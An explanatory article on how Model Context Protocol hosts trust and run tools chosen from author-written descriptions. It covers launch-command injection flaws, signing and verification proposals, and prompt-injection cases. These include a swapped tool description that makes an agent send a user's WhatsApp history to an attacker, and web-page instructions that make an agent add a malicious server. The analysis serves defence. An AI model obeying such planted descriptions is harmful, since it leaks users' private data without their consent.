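# Tool trust in the Model Context Protocol: running unverified code chosen from its description

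## How MCP tools are described, chosen and run

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside programs and data. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, released it on 25 November 2024 so that one shared protocol could replace the custom connector that each new data source needed (*Introducing the Model Context Protocol*, 2024). A language model on its own only produces text, but through MCP it can have a separate program look up a customer record, edit a file or send an email.

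Other AI companies soon adopted the protocol, including OpenAI in March 2025, and in December 2025 Anthropic gave it to a fund under the Linux Foundation. By July 2026, developers were downloading its software development kits, the libraries for building on it, more than 400 million times a month, according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026). Automated builds inflate this figure, so the number of available programs may be a better guide. In *Understanding the Hierarchical Structure and Functional Landscape of the Model Context Protocol*, Tang, Chen and Xiao (2026) gathered listings from 17 marketplaces and found 124,267 distinct projects with 1.33 million tools. Their count excludes closed services because it covers only projects whose source code they could retrieve. About 85% of the tools serve fields other than software development. In *Two Years of MCP Builders*,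 Soria Parra and Delimarsky (2026) reported that more than 2,500 people had contributed to the protocol by its second anniversary in November 2026.

An AI application chooses a tool based on a short description that the tool's author wrote. The protocol's messages do not prove that the code matches this description, that nobody has altered the code, or that it comes from the named publisher.

### Host, client, server and model

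The host is the application that the user runs, such as a chat program or a coding assistant like Cursor. It supplies everything the model reads and carries out what the model returns, though the model itself often runs on its developer's machines. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to a host through the protocol. It can run on a remote machine or on the user's own laptop. The host creates an internal connector, called a client, for each server. Client and server exchange messages in JSON-RPC 2.0, a text format in which each request has a method name and an identifier, and the reply repeats the identifier.

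The model and the server communicate only through the host. Li and Gao (2025), in *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol Ecosystem*, traced the traffic in four desktop hosts, Cursor, Windsurf, Cline and Claude Desktop. Each request to the model consisted of the host's standing instructions, the list of tools and the conversation so far. The model returned a tool's name and arguments, and the host called the tool without independently checking the choice. If the model named a tool that no longer existed and appeared only in the conversation history, the host still tried to call it.

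The model receives a tool's description, which consists of its name, input schema and natural-language text. The protocol does not show the model the tool's implementation, which is the code that runs when the server starts or when the host calls the tool.

### One weather tool, from registry to result

The protocol's documentation mentions a package named `weather-mcp` and, separately, a tool named `get_weather`. Together, they make a harmless weather server whose full lifecycle is easy to follow.

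A user who wants weather reports in a coding assistant first has to find the weather server. Registries are public catalogues of such servers. The official one was still in preview in July 2026. According to Model Context Protocol's *The MCP Registry*, its entries contain metadata, not code: the server's name, a description, where to get it and how to start it. The entry for version 1.2.0 of the weather server points to `weather-mcp` on npm, the main public store of JavaScript packages, where the code is kept. Marketplaces copy these entries, add ratings or make their own selection, and present them to users.

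The user then adds the server to the host's configuration. The new entry contains a command and its arguments for a local server, or a web address for a remote one. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi, 2026) examined 1,723 host applications on GitHub and found that 85.2% keep their list of servers in a file, although developers have not agreed on a common name for it. Package managers have fixed rules for declaring and fetching ordinary software libraries. MCP has no equivalent, and each host follows its own conventions.

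The client runs the command when the host next starts or when the user switches the new entry on. This local mode of MCP is called the stdio transport, after the standard input and output streams that every process has. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026), the part of the specification for this mode, states that the client launches the server as a subprocess, writes requests to its input and reads replies from its output. The weather server now runs as an ordinary program on the user's machine.

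A remote weather server would skip this step because its operator has already started it elsewhere. The client reaches it over Streamable HTTP, which sends each message as a web request to a single address, according to the transport page of the Model Context Protocol specification. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) requires messages to mean the same on either transport. The model uses the same kind of definition in both cases.

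Next the client sends a `tools/list` request, and the server replies with a definition of each tool. The definition below is adapted from the example in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), with comments added to show where each part goes.

```jsonc
{
  "name": "get_weather",            // to the model
  "description":                    // to the model
    "Get current weather information for a location",
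  "inputSchema": {                  // to the model, all of it
    "type": "object",
    "required": ["location"],
    "properties": {
      "location": {
        "type": "string",
        "description": "City name or zip code"   // also to the model
      }
    }
  },
  "title": "Weather Information Provider",       // for the user's screen
  "icons": [ { "src": "https://example.com/weather-icon.png" } ]  // same
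}
```

The model relies on a tool's name, description and input schema. The small text beside `location` is part of the schema, so the model reads that too. The title and icons are for display. Hosts differ in how much of the other information they show the user. Li and Gao found that some displays list every tool with its text and parameters, while others show only the server's name, its connection status and a switch. A user can therefore approve a server without reading the text that will guide the model.

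An author may add a schema for the tool's output and annotations, which are hints for the host. Four of them are yes-or-no statements: whether the tool only reads, whether it may destroy something, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether the tool deals with the outside world. A tool with no annotations counts as the riskier case on all four. But the hints come from the same author as the rest of the definition. In a March 2026 blog post, the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) pointed out that a server can declare a tool read-only and delete the user's files anyway.

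Suppose the user asks about the weather in New York. The host sends the question to the model along with the descriptions of the available tools. The model chooses `get_weather` based on its description and returns that name with "New York" as the location. The client sends a `tools/call` request with the same name and argument, and the server runs the corresponding function and returns the text "72°F, partly cloudy". The host adds the text to the conversation, and the model writes its answer. The messages would have looked the same if the server had invented the temperature or had also copied a few documents.

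### Three moments of trust

A user of the weather server takes a risk when installing it, when the host launches it, and when the host calls its tool.

Installation is the decision to add the server to the host. Some hosts reduce it to one click on a link, and until 2025 the specification had no rules for this. *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server Installation* (Delimarsky, 2025) added rules requiring the host to show the exact command in full, warn that it may be dangerous, and get the user's agreement before running anything. The user sees the command but not the program it fetches. Delimarsky also concedes that people may approve a malicious command despite the warning, and that a capable attacker may write one that looks legitimate.

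Launching a server needs no further decision by the user or the model, and for a local server it is when someone else's code first runs as the server. The process is already running before the client sends `tools/list`, and so before the model has read the tool's description or chosen the tool. The server program itself outputs the tool definition, so the host cannot receive the definition from the server unless the program is running. Code hidden in the weather server to copy the user's files could do so at start-up, even if the user never asked about the weather. The server launches again whenever the host restarts, and under the stdio rules the client should also relaunch a server that exits unexpectedly.

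Users are most likely to notice the call itself, because the host may ask for permission at this step. The four desktop hosts that Li and Gao studied ask before each call by default, but they also have an auto-run mode that skips the request. In the larger sample of Majeed and colleagues, 90.8% of the applications log at least some activity and 77.2% let users enable or disable servers or tools, but only 37.2% wait for approval before running a call. NextChat, an open-source chat application, passes the model's request straight to the tool and only logs it. The sample consists of GitHub repositories with at least ten stars, weighted equally regardless of how many people use them, so these percentages don't measure the share of users who have no approval step.

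The overview of the Model Context Protocol specification equates tools with arbitrary code execution, meaning that a tool may do anything a program can do, and states that hosts must obtain consent before invoking one. This requirement is weaker than it first appears, because the "must" is in lower case and the same page gives the word binding force only in capitals. The corresponding rule on the tools page is that a human SHOULD always be able to deny a call. The maintainers also acknowledge in the overview that the protocol itself cannot enforce such principles.

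Approval at the time of a call can, for instance, keep the host from sending a private document to the weather server as an argument. But it comes too late to prevent anything a local server did at launch. Launch poses less risk to the user with a remote server, because the server starts on the operator's machine. The user's exposure then lies mainly in what the host sends and what it gets back.

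### Why the choice rests on the description

MCP exists to let a host use a tool from an author it has no arrangement with, in a programming language it does not support. The agent therefore relies on a name, some text and a schema, which a ten-line script and a bank's internal system can both supply, although reading the tool's code first would seem safer.

Source code is far less uniform. Tang and colleagues started from the code and traced it to the tools, the reverse of what a host does. They needed a separate analyser for each of seven programming languages, which together covered 88.9% of the projects, and each language had several ways of registering a tool. This step only located the tools and the functions behind them, and it is harder to establish what those functions do when they run.

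An agent often has no access to the code behind a tool. A remote server returns replies without exposing its source code, and the official registry accepts closed-source servers as long as the public can install or reach them. A host could inspect a local package, since it is on the user's disk. But while the definition of `get_weather` takes up a few lines, the program behind it may use libraries many times its own size, and reading all of that code before every call would take an agent far more time and money than getting the weather report.

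Even the short definitions take enough processing that the protocol's designers have tried to reduce it. Since July 2026, servers should return their tools in a fixed order, partly so that a model provider can reuse its processing of text it has seen before. The server also specifies how long the client may treat each list as fresh (five minutes in the weather example). Reading the code once per version would take much less processing than reading it at every call, but it would require a reliable way to tell that the version has not changed.

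Many tools do the same job. Tang and colleagues found 18 tools from different servers for sending an email through Gmail, with names like `send_via_gmail` and `gmail_send`. Some of the projects had no GitHub stars, a rough measure of popularity, while one had 1,015. One had last been updated 15 days earlier, another 480 days earlier. By their count, 98.5% of all tools have at least one alternative that does the same job, though this figure is approximate because only 85% of the grouped tool pairs they checked proved comparable. The tool definitions include none of this background on the projects, so a model choosing among these tools has to go by the wording.

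A tool's description comes with no proof that it is accurate. The tool definition has no field for the source code's location, a hash of the code (a short fingerprint that changes whenever the code changes) or a publisher's signature. Servers should give their name with each result, but the author can choose any name, and the specification advises hosts not to rely on it even to tell two servers apart.

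The newest version of the protocol, dated 28 July 2026, is a large revision, but nothing in the list of changes from the Model Context Protocol (2026) project ties a tool's description to its implementation. The changes include removing the opening handshake and sessions, caching tool lists, and making authorization stricter. Authorization controls which users and applications may use a server, but not what the server's code does with a request. In August, a roadmap from the Model Context Protocol (2026) maintainers still listed the next release as upcoming.

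Some proposals could reveal when a tool definition has been altered. SEP-1766 would have hosts compare tool definitions with recorded hashes. It was still an open proposal on 1 May 2026, according to *ADR-004* (2026), a design note from MCP Hangar, a project that monitors and filters MCP traffic. It does not appear among the July changes. Sharif's *MCPS* (2026) proposes wrapping the protocol in an envelope of signed messages and protected tool definitions, leaving the core unchanged. Such measures would not show whether the original definition was true.

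### Four separate questions

"Can this tool be trusted?" runs together four questions, and a good answer to one of them may leave the others wide open.

Provenance is evidence of who published the code and how they built it. The official registry covers only who published it. Each server name there begins with a GitHub account or a web domain, as in `io.github.username/server`, and only the holder of that account or domain can publish under it. For npm packages, Model Context Protocol's *MCP Registry Supported Package Types* also requires the package to contain the same server name as the registry entry, so a stranger cannot simply list somebody else's package as their own. The user of `weather-mcp` can therefore find out which account published it, but not whether the person behind the account is honest or still controls it.

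Hashes are the usual way to check a package's integrity, meaning that its code is unchanged. The registry requires a hash only for MCPB bundles, which are files that users download from GitHub or GitLab. The client, not the registry, verifies the hash before installation. An npm entry, such as the one for the weather server, needs a version number but no hash. A matching hash means only that the user received the file the publisher meant to send, so it will still match if the publisher put malicious code in the file.

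A description-code inconsistency is a difference between a tool's description and what its code does. The description may leave something out. For example, a `get_weather` tool could return correct forecasts, matching its one-line description, and also upload the user's documents. The official registry does not examine code, and its maintainers leave security scanning to the package stores and marketplaces.

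A sandbox limits which files, network addresses and system functions a program can reach. It would let the weather server contact its weather service and nothing else. This limit would hold even if the author was dishonest or somebody had tampered with the package, but it would not make the forecasts correct.

A local server normally runs with the privileges of the user whose desktop host launches it. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* warns that an attacker who gets malicious code into a local server can run any command with the client's privileges. It requires a consent dialog before a one-click installation, but recommends a sandbox with minimal rights only as a SHOULD. Without a sandbox, a weather server that needs one web address can read every file its user can read, and on a developer's machine those files often include the keys to other systems.

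## The view that trust is decided when a server is installed

On one view, users decide whether to trust a local MCP server when they install it. The user chooses which programs to run, the host prompts the user for approval before it does something risky, and the protocol only carries messages. The MCP project's documents largely take this view. In 2026 Anthropic defended a version of it when a security company demanded changes to how the protocol's software launches local servers.

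### Why a protocol might leave verification to others

The best technical argument for this view is that a local server is already running when it sends its first message, so any information in that message about the server's code comes from the code itself. A malicious program could send a false hash or another program's genuine signature. A useful check therefore has to happen before launch, when only the user, the host and the package store can act.

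The maintainers apply this reasoning to bug reports. According to Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy*, a malicious server "already has arbitrary code execution by virtue of being run", and the stdio transport "is not a sandbox". They therefore list attacks between a local client and its server as intentional behavior, not as vulnerabilities. Anyone who wants to restrict a local server's privileges has to enforce the restriction themselves.

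A protocol also cannot determine which programs a particular user considers safe. A user would be alarmed if a weather server deleted files, but a disk-cleaning tool is meant to delete them. A company's own database server may not appear in any public registry, yet the company's developers have more reason to trust it than a popular package from a stranger. If the protocol permitted only approved programs, somebody would have to maintain the list, and MCP would lose its ability to connect any host to any tool.

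Developers already take this risk when they install an npm package or a code editor extension, which also runs other people's code, usually with all of the developer's own privileges. The security firm ARMO compared MCP's local servers with `git clone` and `npm install`, everyday commands for fetching such code, according to Patch Day Alert's *Anthropic's MCP gives every downstream app unauthenticated RCE*.

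The argument is older than MCP. In the comments on a Microsoft developer blog post (2023) about "attacks" that consist of changing a user's files, one reader objected that a person who edits a configuration file they already control is only attacking themselves. Another noted that attacker and victim can be different people, for example when an administrator has access to everyone's files. The installation view is strongest when one person owns the machine, edits the configuration and bears the damage.

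### Consent in the specification

If the protocol does not verify tools, much depends on the user's consent. The trust principles in Model Context Protocol (2025), the November 2025 revision, require users to "explicitly consent to and understand all data access and operations". Under these principles, tools "represent arbitrary code execution" and call for caution, and hosts should treat descriptions of tool behavior as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. According to the July 2026 revision, the protocol still cannot enforce such principles.

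The rule about descriptions is useful only if the host has a way to tell which servers to trust, and the principles don't provide one. In practice, the user decides by installing the server, and that one decision determines whether the host may trust everything the server later sends about its tools.

The maintainers have extended consent to new features. MCP Apps, an official extension released with the July revision, lets a server supply an interactive page for the host to display. Model Context Protocol (2026) explains that hosts show the page in a sandboxed frame, and that any action it triggers goes through the same consent path as an ordinary tool call. Tools declare these pages so that hosts can review them before anything runs. The stdio transport has no comparable step for reviewing the server program itself, which is far more powerful than the page.

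Kale (2026), in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential*, argues that the July revision moves enforcement further from the protocol and onto the organizations that run MCP software and the developers who build it. Kale, who builds agent systems for companies, warns that those who don't adapt will inherit weaknesses that their network security tools cannot detect.

Consent also comes too late to cover tool descriptions. The security firm Trail of Bits pointed out in *Jumping the line* (2025) that a tool's description reaches the model before the user has approved any call, so a malicious description can influence the model even if the user never agrees to run the tool. The model might then suggest a command with a harmful addition. Asking the user to approve the command offers little protection, because a developer working in an unfamiliar language is unlikely to notice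 the addition.

### The dispute over launch commands

In November 2025, researchers at OX Security, which sells security tools for software developers, began studying MCP software. One program they examined, GPT Researcher, is an open-source research assistant that let users add a local MCP server by entering the command to start it. ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector* reports that any operating system command entered there ran on the machine hosting the application. The researchers first blamed an adapter from LangChain, which makes libraries for building agents, and then traced the behavior to the MCP software development kits (SDKs) that Anthropic created.

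The SDK's launch function takes a command and its arguments, starts the command as a process, and then tries to communicate with it as an MCP server. If the process replies correctly, the application gets a working connection. Otherwise the application gets an error, but the command has already run. The function accepts any command, and it could hardly check whether an unknown program is an MCP server without starting it.

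Whether this is dangerous depends on where the command comes from. The two cases below, adapted from OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains*, look almost the same in code.

```python
# The developer writes the command into the program
StdioServerParameters(command="python", args=["myapp.py"])

# The command comes from a form that other people can fill in
StdioServerParameters(command=form_command, args=form_arguments)
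```

The first version gives an outsider nothing to change, but the second lets anyone who can fill in the form run programs on the machine.

OX Security's *MCP Supply Chain Advisory* describes several ways outsiders could get this control. LangFlow, an open-source AI framework owned by IBM, gave any visitor a session token and then accepted a launch command from them. The researchers found 915 LangFlow installations reachable from the internet. Letta AI, a platform for agents with long-term memory, offered only remote servers in its interface, but its back end accepted a stdio configuration if an attacker altered the request.

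Two other projects, Flowise and Upsonic, had already tried to prevent this problem by allowing only a few familiar programs. Some of those programs accept arguments that make them run other commands, so an attacker could bypass the filter.

The coding assistant Windsurf had a different weakness. Its agent can edit the file that lists its MCP servers, so an agent that read a web page with hidden instructions could add a new server to the file, and Windsurf would run that server's command without any further action by the user. OX Security reported the same problem in Cursor, Claude Code, Gemini-CLI and GitHub Copilot, but these need at least one user interaction before the file changes. The researchers also placed a harmless test package in nine of 11 MCP registries.

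OX Security published its results on 15 April 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Systemic Flaw in MCP Protocol Could Expose 150 Million Downloads*. The figures in its announcement, *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers*, differ a good deal in how much evidence supports them. The researchers executed commands on six live platforms. They made more than 30 disclosures to vendors and maintainers, which led to at least ten CVEs, entries in the public catalog of software vulnerabilities. They also counted more than 7,000 publicly reachable servers and extrapolated from that count to as many as 200,000 vulnerable instances, as VentureBeat's *200,000 MCP servers expose a command execution flaw* explains.

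The figure of 150 million downloads is the weakest measure of exposure. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, a blog post whose author promotes his own security gateway for agents, breaks the total into 73 million for the Python SDK, 57 million for LiteLLM, which connects applications to many models, and 22 million for FastMCP, a library for building MCP software. FastMCP builds on the SDK, so one installation can count twice. Automated builds and mirrors inflate the figure further, as Patch Day Alert notes. More importantly, a download of the SDK is only a problem if the application lets someone untrusted choose the launch command. VentureBeat's claim that any team using the default stdio transport is exposed is too broad for the same reason.

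### What OX Security wanted and what Anthropic answered

OX Security wanted Anthropic to fix the problem once in the SDKs, so that every application built on them would benefit. flyingpenguin lists four proposals:

- Applications would launch only what a manifest declares, instead of accepting any command.
- The SDKs would block high-risk programs by default through a list of permitted commands.
- Developers would have to switch on a "dangerous mode" before using arguments that change at run time.
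- Marketplaces would require a security manifest signed by a developer whose identity they had verified.

The dangerous-mode setting would alert developers to the risk but would block nothing once they had switched it on. A list of permitted commands would stop the crudest attacks, but the company's own attack on Flowise succeeded using a permitted program, which is a reason not to rely on such a list. Launching servers only from a manifest would be stricter, provided that an attacker could not also write the manifest.

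Anthropic declined to change the design. Reports of its reasons mix its own words with those of its critics. VentureBeat found that "expected" was the only word Anthropic had stated on the record, and got no reply to its request for comment. Two longer statements became public through OX Security. In the one ITPro printed, Anthropic rejects the report because the attack "requires explicit user permission for the file change". This fits coding assistants, which ask before editing a configuration file, better than a web form. In the other, printed by flyingpenguin, Anthropic says of the transport itself that "we believe that this design does represent a secure default".

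The position that developers are responsible for sanitizing input, which most coverage attributes to Anthropic, is OX Security's paraphrase. Among the replies flyingpenguin quotes, the closest to it is from LangChain, which holds application authors responsible for checking input from untrusted sources. Anthropic moved toward this position nine days after the researchers first contacted it in January 2026, when it updated the project's security policy to advise caution with stdio adapters. The researchers replied that this fixed nothing.

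Other companies sided with Anthropic, at least in how they handled the reports. FastMCP's maintainers replied that the stdio transport is meant to start a subprocess. Cursor pointed out that users click to accept edits to the configuration. OX Security's advisory also lists its disclosures to Amazon, NVIDIA and GitHub Copilot as rejected. Some vendors argued that they already ran the commands in a sandbox. The researchers accepted that this protects other customers' data, but noted that an attacker could still use the machine to mine cryptocurrency or relay traffic.

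VentureBeat set out the fullest defense of the design, while Anthropic gave only a single word. The defense is that anyone who can write to the configuration file already has authority to run programs on that machine. It adds that a restriction in the protocol would either break a transport whose job is to launch local programs or move the attack into the launched program. Carter Rees, an AI executive at the company Reputation, told VentureBeat that this argument is consistent but fails in practice. He argued that a mistake repeated in so many independent products is no longer just a developer's mistake.

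The defense works for a developer who configures their own laptop, but not for LangFlow, where a stranger may enter the command, or for Windsurf, where a web page can in effect write the configuration entry. The security firm Cantina rightly says that a product gives untrusted input a path to running local programs as soon as it lets a model, a user's data or a writable file influence the launch fields. Applications can prevent this without any change to MCP, but a safer default in the SDKs would have helped those that did not. By 1 May 2026, only some of the affected products had released fixes.

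None of this concerns false tool descriptions. An attacker who controls the launch command doesn't need a tool, a description, or even a working MCP server. Conversely, suppose a developer writes the command for a weather server into the configuration and nobody changes it. If the server copies documents as well as reporting the temperature, all the proposed SDK changes would let it run. Signed manifests in marketplaces would identify its author but would not reveal the copying.

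### How far the comparison with packages goes

The comparison with package managers is accurate for the code itself. A malicious local MCP server can do the same damage as a malicious npm package with the same privileges, and neither npm nor MCP verifies that code does what its description says. If developers accept this risk with npm, it seems odd to demand that MCP eliminate it.

The comparison is weaker after installation. A developer who installs a library decides where to call it and writes that call into a program. Colleagues can review the call, and it stays there until someone edits the program. An MCP host instead gives the model the list of available tools with each request, and the model selects which ones to use each time.

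Suppose a developer installs the weather server while planning a trip, then a week later asks the same assistant to find a bug in a payment system. If the server is still switched on, the model reads its description again while working on the payment code. The developer trusted the server to report the weather, and probably never considered how its text could affect a conversation about payments. A misleading tool description can affect every later task, whereas a misleading summary on a package's web page mostly affects people who read it before installing.

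A tool's description may change after the server is installed. tianpan.co's *Your Tool Descriptions Are an Instruction Channel the Model Obeys* (2026) emphasizes that the server returns the description at run time, and that the protocol has no standard way to guarantee that it matches what a person reviewed at installation. According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), tool lists no longer vary from one connection to another under the July revision. A server can still return a different list later, though. Developers can guard against changes to a package by pinning it, which means recording the exact version or hash they approved and refusing anything else, but a remote server gives them no package to pin.

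The view that trust is decided at installation assumes that a person makes the decision. In Windsurf, an agent could carry out the installation, which also undermines the comparison.

Defenders of this view could answer that hosts can address much of the risk without a new protocol by showing users each tool description and alerting them when the text changes. These alerts would miss a change in the code if the description stayed the same. The MCP project has not settled the question. The charter for its Security Interest Group, a forum for reviewing threats and proposals, includes working out how a server should prove its identity before a client sends it any work.

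### Willison's argument about mixing tools and text

The software developer Simon Willison argues in *Model Context Protocol has prompt injection security problems* (2025) that the main danger arises whenever a language model has tools that can act for the user and also reads text from people the user has no reason to trust, with or without MCP. The model cannot reliably distinguish the user's instructions from instructions somebody else has hidden in that text, a weakness known as prompt injection.

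His main example is a server that connects an assistant to a personal WhatsApp account and can list, search and send messages. The security company Invariant Labs had shown that a second, malicious server could steal the user's message history through it. The malicious server first offered a harmless tool that gave a fact of the day, then replaced the tool's description with instructions about how to send WhatsApp messages. The model would follow these and send the history to the attacker's number using the WhatsApp server's sending tool. Extra spaces pushed the stolen text off the edge of Cursor's approval window, so a user who looked at the request saw only an ordinary message.

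Willison then describes an attack that needs no malicious server, in which a stranger sends the user a WhatsApp message containing similar instructions. The assistant reads the message with one tool and could forward the user's private messages with another. Every tool works as described, and its publisher may be honest. Someone checking the server's code would find nothing wrong.

This partly supports the installation view, because it suggests that proving a tool honest would leave a serious problem unsolved. But it also weakens the idea that users can protect themselves just by choosing servers carefully. The hostile message arrives after installation, and the risk can come from combining tools that each look reasonable alone. The attack is possible when an assistant can read private data, take in outside text and send information out. A host that requests approval for one server at a time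 does not show the user that combination.

Willison wants hosts to show tool descriptions and warn about changes. He thinks this would prevent rug pulls, in which a server changes a tool for the worse after the user has approved it. He also advises developers to treat the specification's SHOULDs on human approval as MUSTs. He offers no solution to prompt injection in general and admits that he has "no idea how to make it universally safe".

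His argument covers only harm that passes through the model. Malicious code that acts at launch can do harm without misleading the model.

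## The view that tools should be verified before they run

People who want tools verified agree with defenders of the installation view that a running program cannot establish that its own code is trustworthy. They draw the stricter conclusion that the host should look for outside evidence about a tool's source, integrity or behavior before running it, and refuse any tool that has none.

Metere (2026), in *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, argues that ordinary web security does not provide this evidence. A web certificate shows that the host reached the address it asked for, and an OAuth login shows the server which user is calling. Neither shows whether the host should accept tools from that server, and an attacker can get a valid certificate for any domain they own. Metere, whose company makes Enclawed, a security-hardened gateway for agents, thinks that one person on a laptop may be able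 to bear this risk but that a bank or a hospital cannot, partly because it would have no record of deciding to admit the server.

Approval can also go out of date. In a scenario from *MCP-38* (2026), a catalog of threats to MCP systems, an attacker replaces the description of a file-reading tool weeks after a security team approved its server.

### Hashes, signatures, pins and attestations

Suppose the publisher of the weather server releases version 1.2.0 as a single file. SHA-256, a common hash function, turns a file of any length into 64 hexadecimal characters. Changing one letter of the code gives a different hash, and nobody knows a practical way to make a second file with the same one. The publisher posts the hash, and the host computes it again from the downloaded file and stops if the two differ. This only works if the host gets the published hash from a place the attacker doesn't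 control, because an attacker who can replace both the file and the hash can make a malicious file pass the check.

A digital signature removes that weakness. The publisher creates two linked keys, keeps the private one secret and shares the public one. The publisher uses the private key to compute a signature for the file. The host then uses the public key to check that the signature matches the file. An attacker who alters the file cannot compute a new valid signature without the private key.

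The host still needs to know whose key it is, because anyone can create a pair of keys and correctly sign a malicious weather server with them. Bernstein's *MCP server signing and supply-chain scan*, the documentation for a small project, describes separate verdicts for an invalid signature and for a valid signature from a key that isn't on the host's trusted list. Somebody has to maintain that list, or rely on a certificate authority to do it.

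Pinning prevents unapproved updates. If the host's configuration specifies version 1.2.0 of the weather server instead of the latest one, the host will not automatically install a malicious version 1.2.1. But the publisher of a container image, a package that includes everything a program needs to run, can usually move a version label such as "1.0.0" to a different image. The official MCP registry therefore also accepts an image's hash in place of the label, according to Model Context Protocol. Any pin also delays security fixes until somebody approves them.

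Hosts can also pin tool descriptions. Trail of Bits' *Model Context Protocol* page describes mcp-context-protector, a free wrapper that records a server's configuration and tool descriptions on first use and holds later changes for manual approval. This cannot help if the server was malicious from the start, or if a local server does its harm at launch.

A build attestation is a signed statement about how a package came to exist. Stacklok's *From unknown to verified* divides it into a subject, a predicate and a signature. For the weather server, a simplified one might look like this:

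```jsonc
{
  "subject": {                     // which file the statement is about
    "name": "weather-mcp-1.2.0.tgz",
    "sha256": "9f2c..."
  },
  "predicate": {                   // how the build service made the file
    "source": "my-username/mcp-weather-server",
    "commit": "41ab...",           // the exact state of the source code
    "builder": "GitHub Actions"
  },
  "signature": "MEUC..."           // made during the build
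}
```

The host checks that the signature comes from a build service it accepts, that the downloaded file's hash matches the one in the attestation, and that the source repository is the one it expects. An attacker who has stolen only the publisher's npm password could upload a malicious package, but could not get an attestation that traces it to the real repository. The attestation also lets a reviewer who has read the source code at the listed commit know that the package was built from it. A package built from malicious code in the repository would still pass all these checks.

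Much of the technology for this verification already exists outside MCP. In *Modern Software Registries are a Trust Service*, Holterhoff (2026) counts provenance and short-lived signing among the services that npm and PyPI, the main store of Python packages, now provide. Stacklok's ToolHive, which runs MCP servers, can check attestations from public and private repositories. Proponents want hosts to require such checks before running a server.

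### ETDI: signing the tool definition

A package hash covers the weather server's files, but the running server could still send any description. In *ETDI*, Bhatt, Narajala and Habler (2025) therefore propose an Enhanced Tool Definition Interface, in which a provider signs a tool's name, description, schemas, version number and required permissions as one unit. Changing any of these requires a new version with a new signature.

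When a server sends its definitions, an ETDI host would go through these steps before showing a tool to the user or the model:

1. Verify the signature with the provider's public key, and reject the tool if this fails.
2. Look up the version and hash that the user last approved. If there are none, ask the user to approve the tool.
3. If the version number is unchanged, compare the hashes. If they differ, log possible tampering and ask the user again.
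4. If the version is newer, ask the user to approve it. If it is older, follow the host's policy on whether to allow, warn or block.
5. Store the approved version, hash and permissions for next time.

This would stop a stranger from copying the wording of `get_weather` and passing the copy off as the original publisher's tool. It would also reveal if someone had added a sentence to the description telling the model to attach the user's files. The third step is oddly lenient because it lets a user click "yes" to accept a definition that has changed without a new version number, even though versions are supposed to be immutable.

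Bhatt and colleagues add two extensions. In one, an identity provider issues a token tied to a particular tool and version, and can later revoke it. In the other, a policy engine decides whether to allow each call based on its context, such as which file the tool would read and for what purpose. They concede that somebody would have to certify that servers and clients do not bypass the engine.

The larger gap is in ETDI's own example of a rug pull. The provider of a "Daily Wallpaper" tool changes its code so that it also searches the user's documents for financial files and uploads them, while the name and version stay the same. To catch this, ETDI adds a hash of the tool's API contract, a machine-readable list of the requests a service accepts and the replies it gives, to the signed definition. But the wallpaper tool can upload documents without changing those requests or replies, so the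 signature, version and contract hash all still match. ETDI protects only what the provider has declared about the tool. It has a working version built on the Python SDK, but the paper argues for its security from the design rather than from attack experiments.

Metere's system, which Enclawed already uses in production, checks the server instead of each tool definition. The server publishes a small signed file at a fixed web address, giving its identity and its clearance, which is the most sensitive class of data it may handle. The host checks that the signing key is on a list its operator set up in advance and is authorized for that clearance. It then verifies the signature and checks that the clearance is high enough for the task. The model can still call only the tools that the operator has listed for that server. In tests, the host refused every forged file and disguised tool name, many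 of which were written by a language model.

Those tests measure whether the gate can be fooled about identity. Metere acknowledges that an admitted server can still misbehave within its permitted tools. Adoption is also a problem. Google publishes no such file for its Gmail server, so Enclawed connects to it through its own signed connector, which has a fixed list of tools for reading and drafting mail.

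### TrustDesc: writing the description from the code

Even when a tool is signed, its author still decides what its description says. *TRUSTDESC* (Ye, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) discards that description and has a language model write a new one from the tool's source code.

The TrustDesc system first collects the relevant code in a stage called SliceMin. It finds the function that handles calls to the tool, follows every function this one calls, and asks a language model to cut the parts that the tool can never reach. For example, a paper-search tool in the study uses a helper function that can filter papers by year, but the tool never passes it a year. Without this step, a model that read the whole helper might describe a filter that users of the tool cannot use.

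The next stage, DescGen, drafts the description. A tool's author can no longer write the description but might try to influence it through the code, so DescGen deletes all comments, cuts function and variable names to 20 characters, and removes promotional words from those names.

DynVer then tests the draft. A language model turns each checkable statement into a task, an agent carries out the task with the tool, and a model acting as judge reads the logs. One draft included the statement that a spreadsheet tool would add a missing equals sign to a formula. The test run ended in an error, and DynVer removed the statement.

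Ye and colleagues tried this on 52 tools from 12 MCP servers, with 208 tasks. An agent completed 175 tasks (84.1%) using the original descriptions and an average of 182.5 (87.7%) using the generated ones. Half of the tasks came from the generated descriptions, which may have given those descriptions an advantage, so the safest conclusion is that replacing the originals did not lower the agent's success rate. Generating a description with Gemini 3 Flash, Google's inexpensive model, cost 1.3 cents and took about 26 seconds. The researchers also collected seven published examples of poisoned descriptions, and the generated replacements contained none of the harmful or promotional wording.

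The generated text sometimes included useful warnings that the tool's author had left out. For example, the spreadsheet tool blocks certain unsafe formulas, but its original description omitted this. The agent tried one, got an error, and wrote the same formula into the sheet with a different tool that lacked this check. When the description included the restriction, the model could refuse the task at the start.

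TrustDesc depends on strong assumptions. It needs the source code, which rules out closed-source servers and most remote ones. Ye and colleagues also assume that the code contains no overtly malicious behavior, which they leave to malware scanners. This is a large exclusion for anyone worried about a weather server that copies documents. If the server copies them at start-up, the function that handles weather requests never calls the copying code, so SliceMin would not collect it. SliceMin also records calls to outside libraries without examining the libraries' code, so it would miss a malicious library too. DynVer has to run the tool, so verifying it safely would require a sandbox.

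### Adoption by registries and hosts

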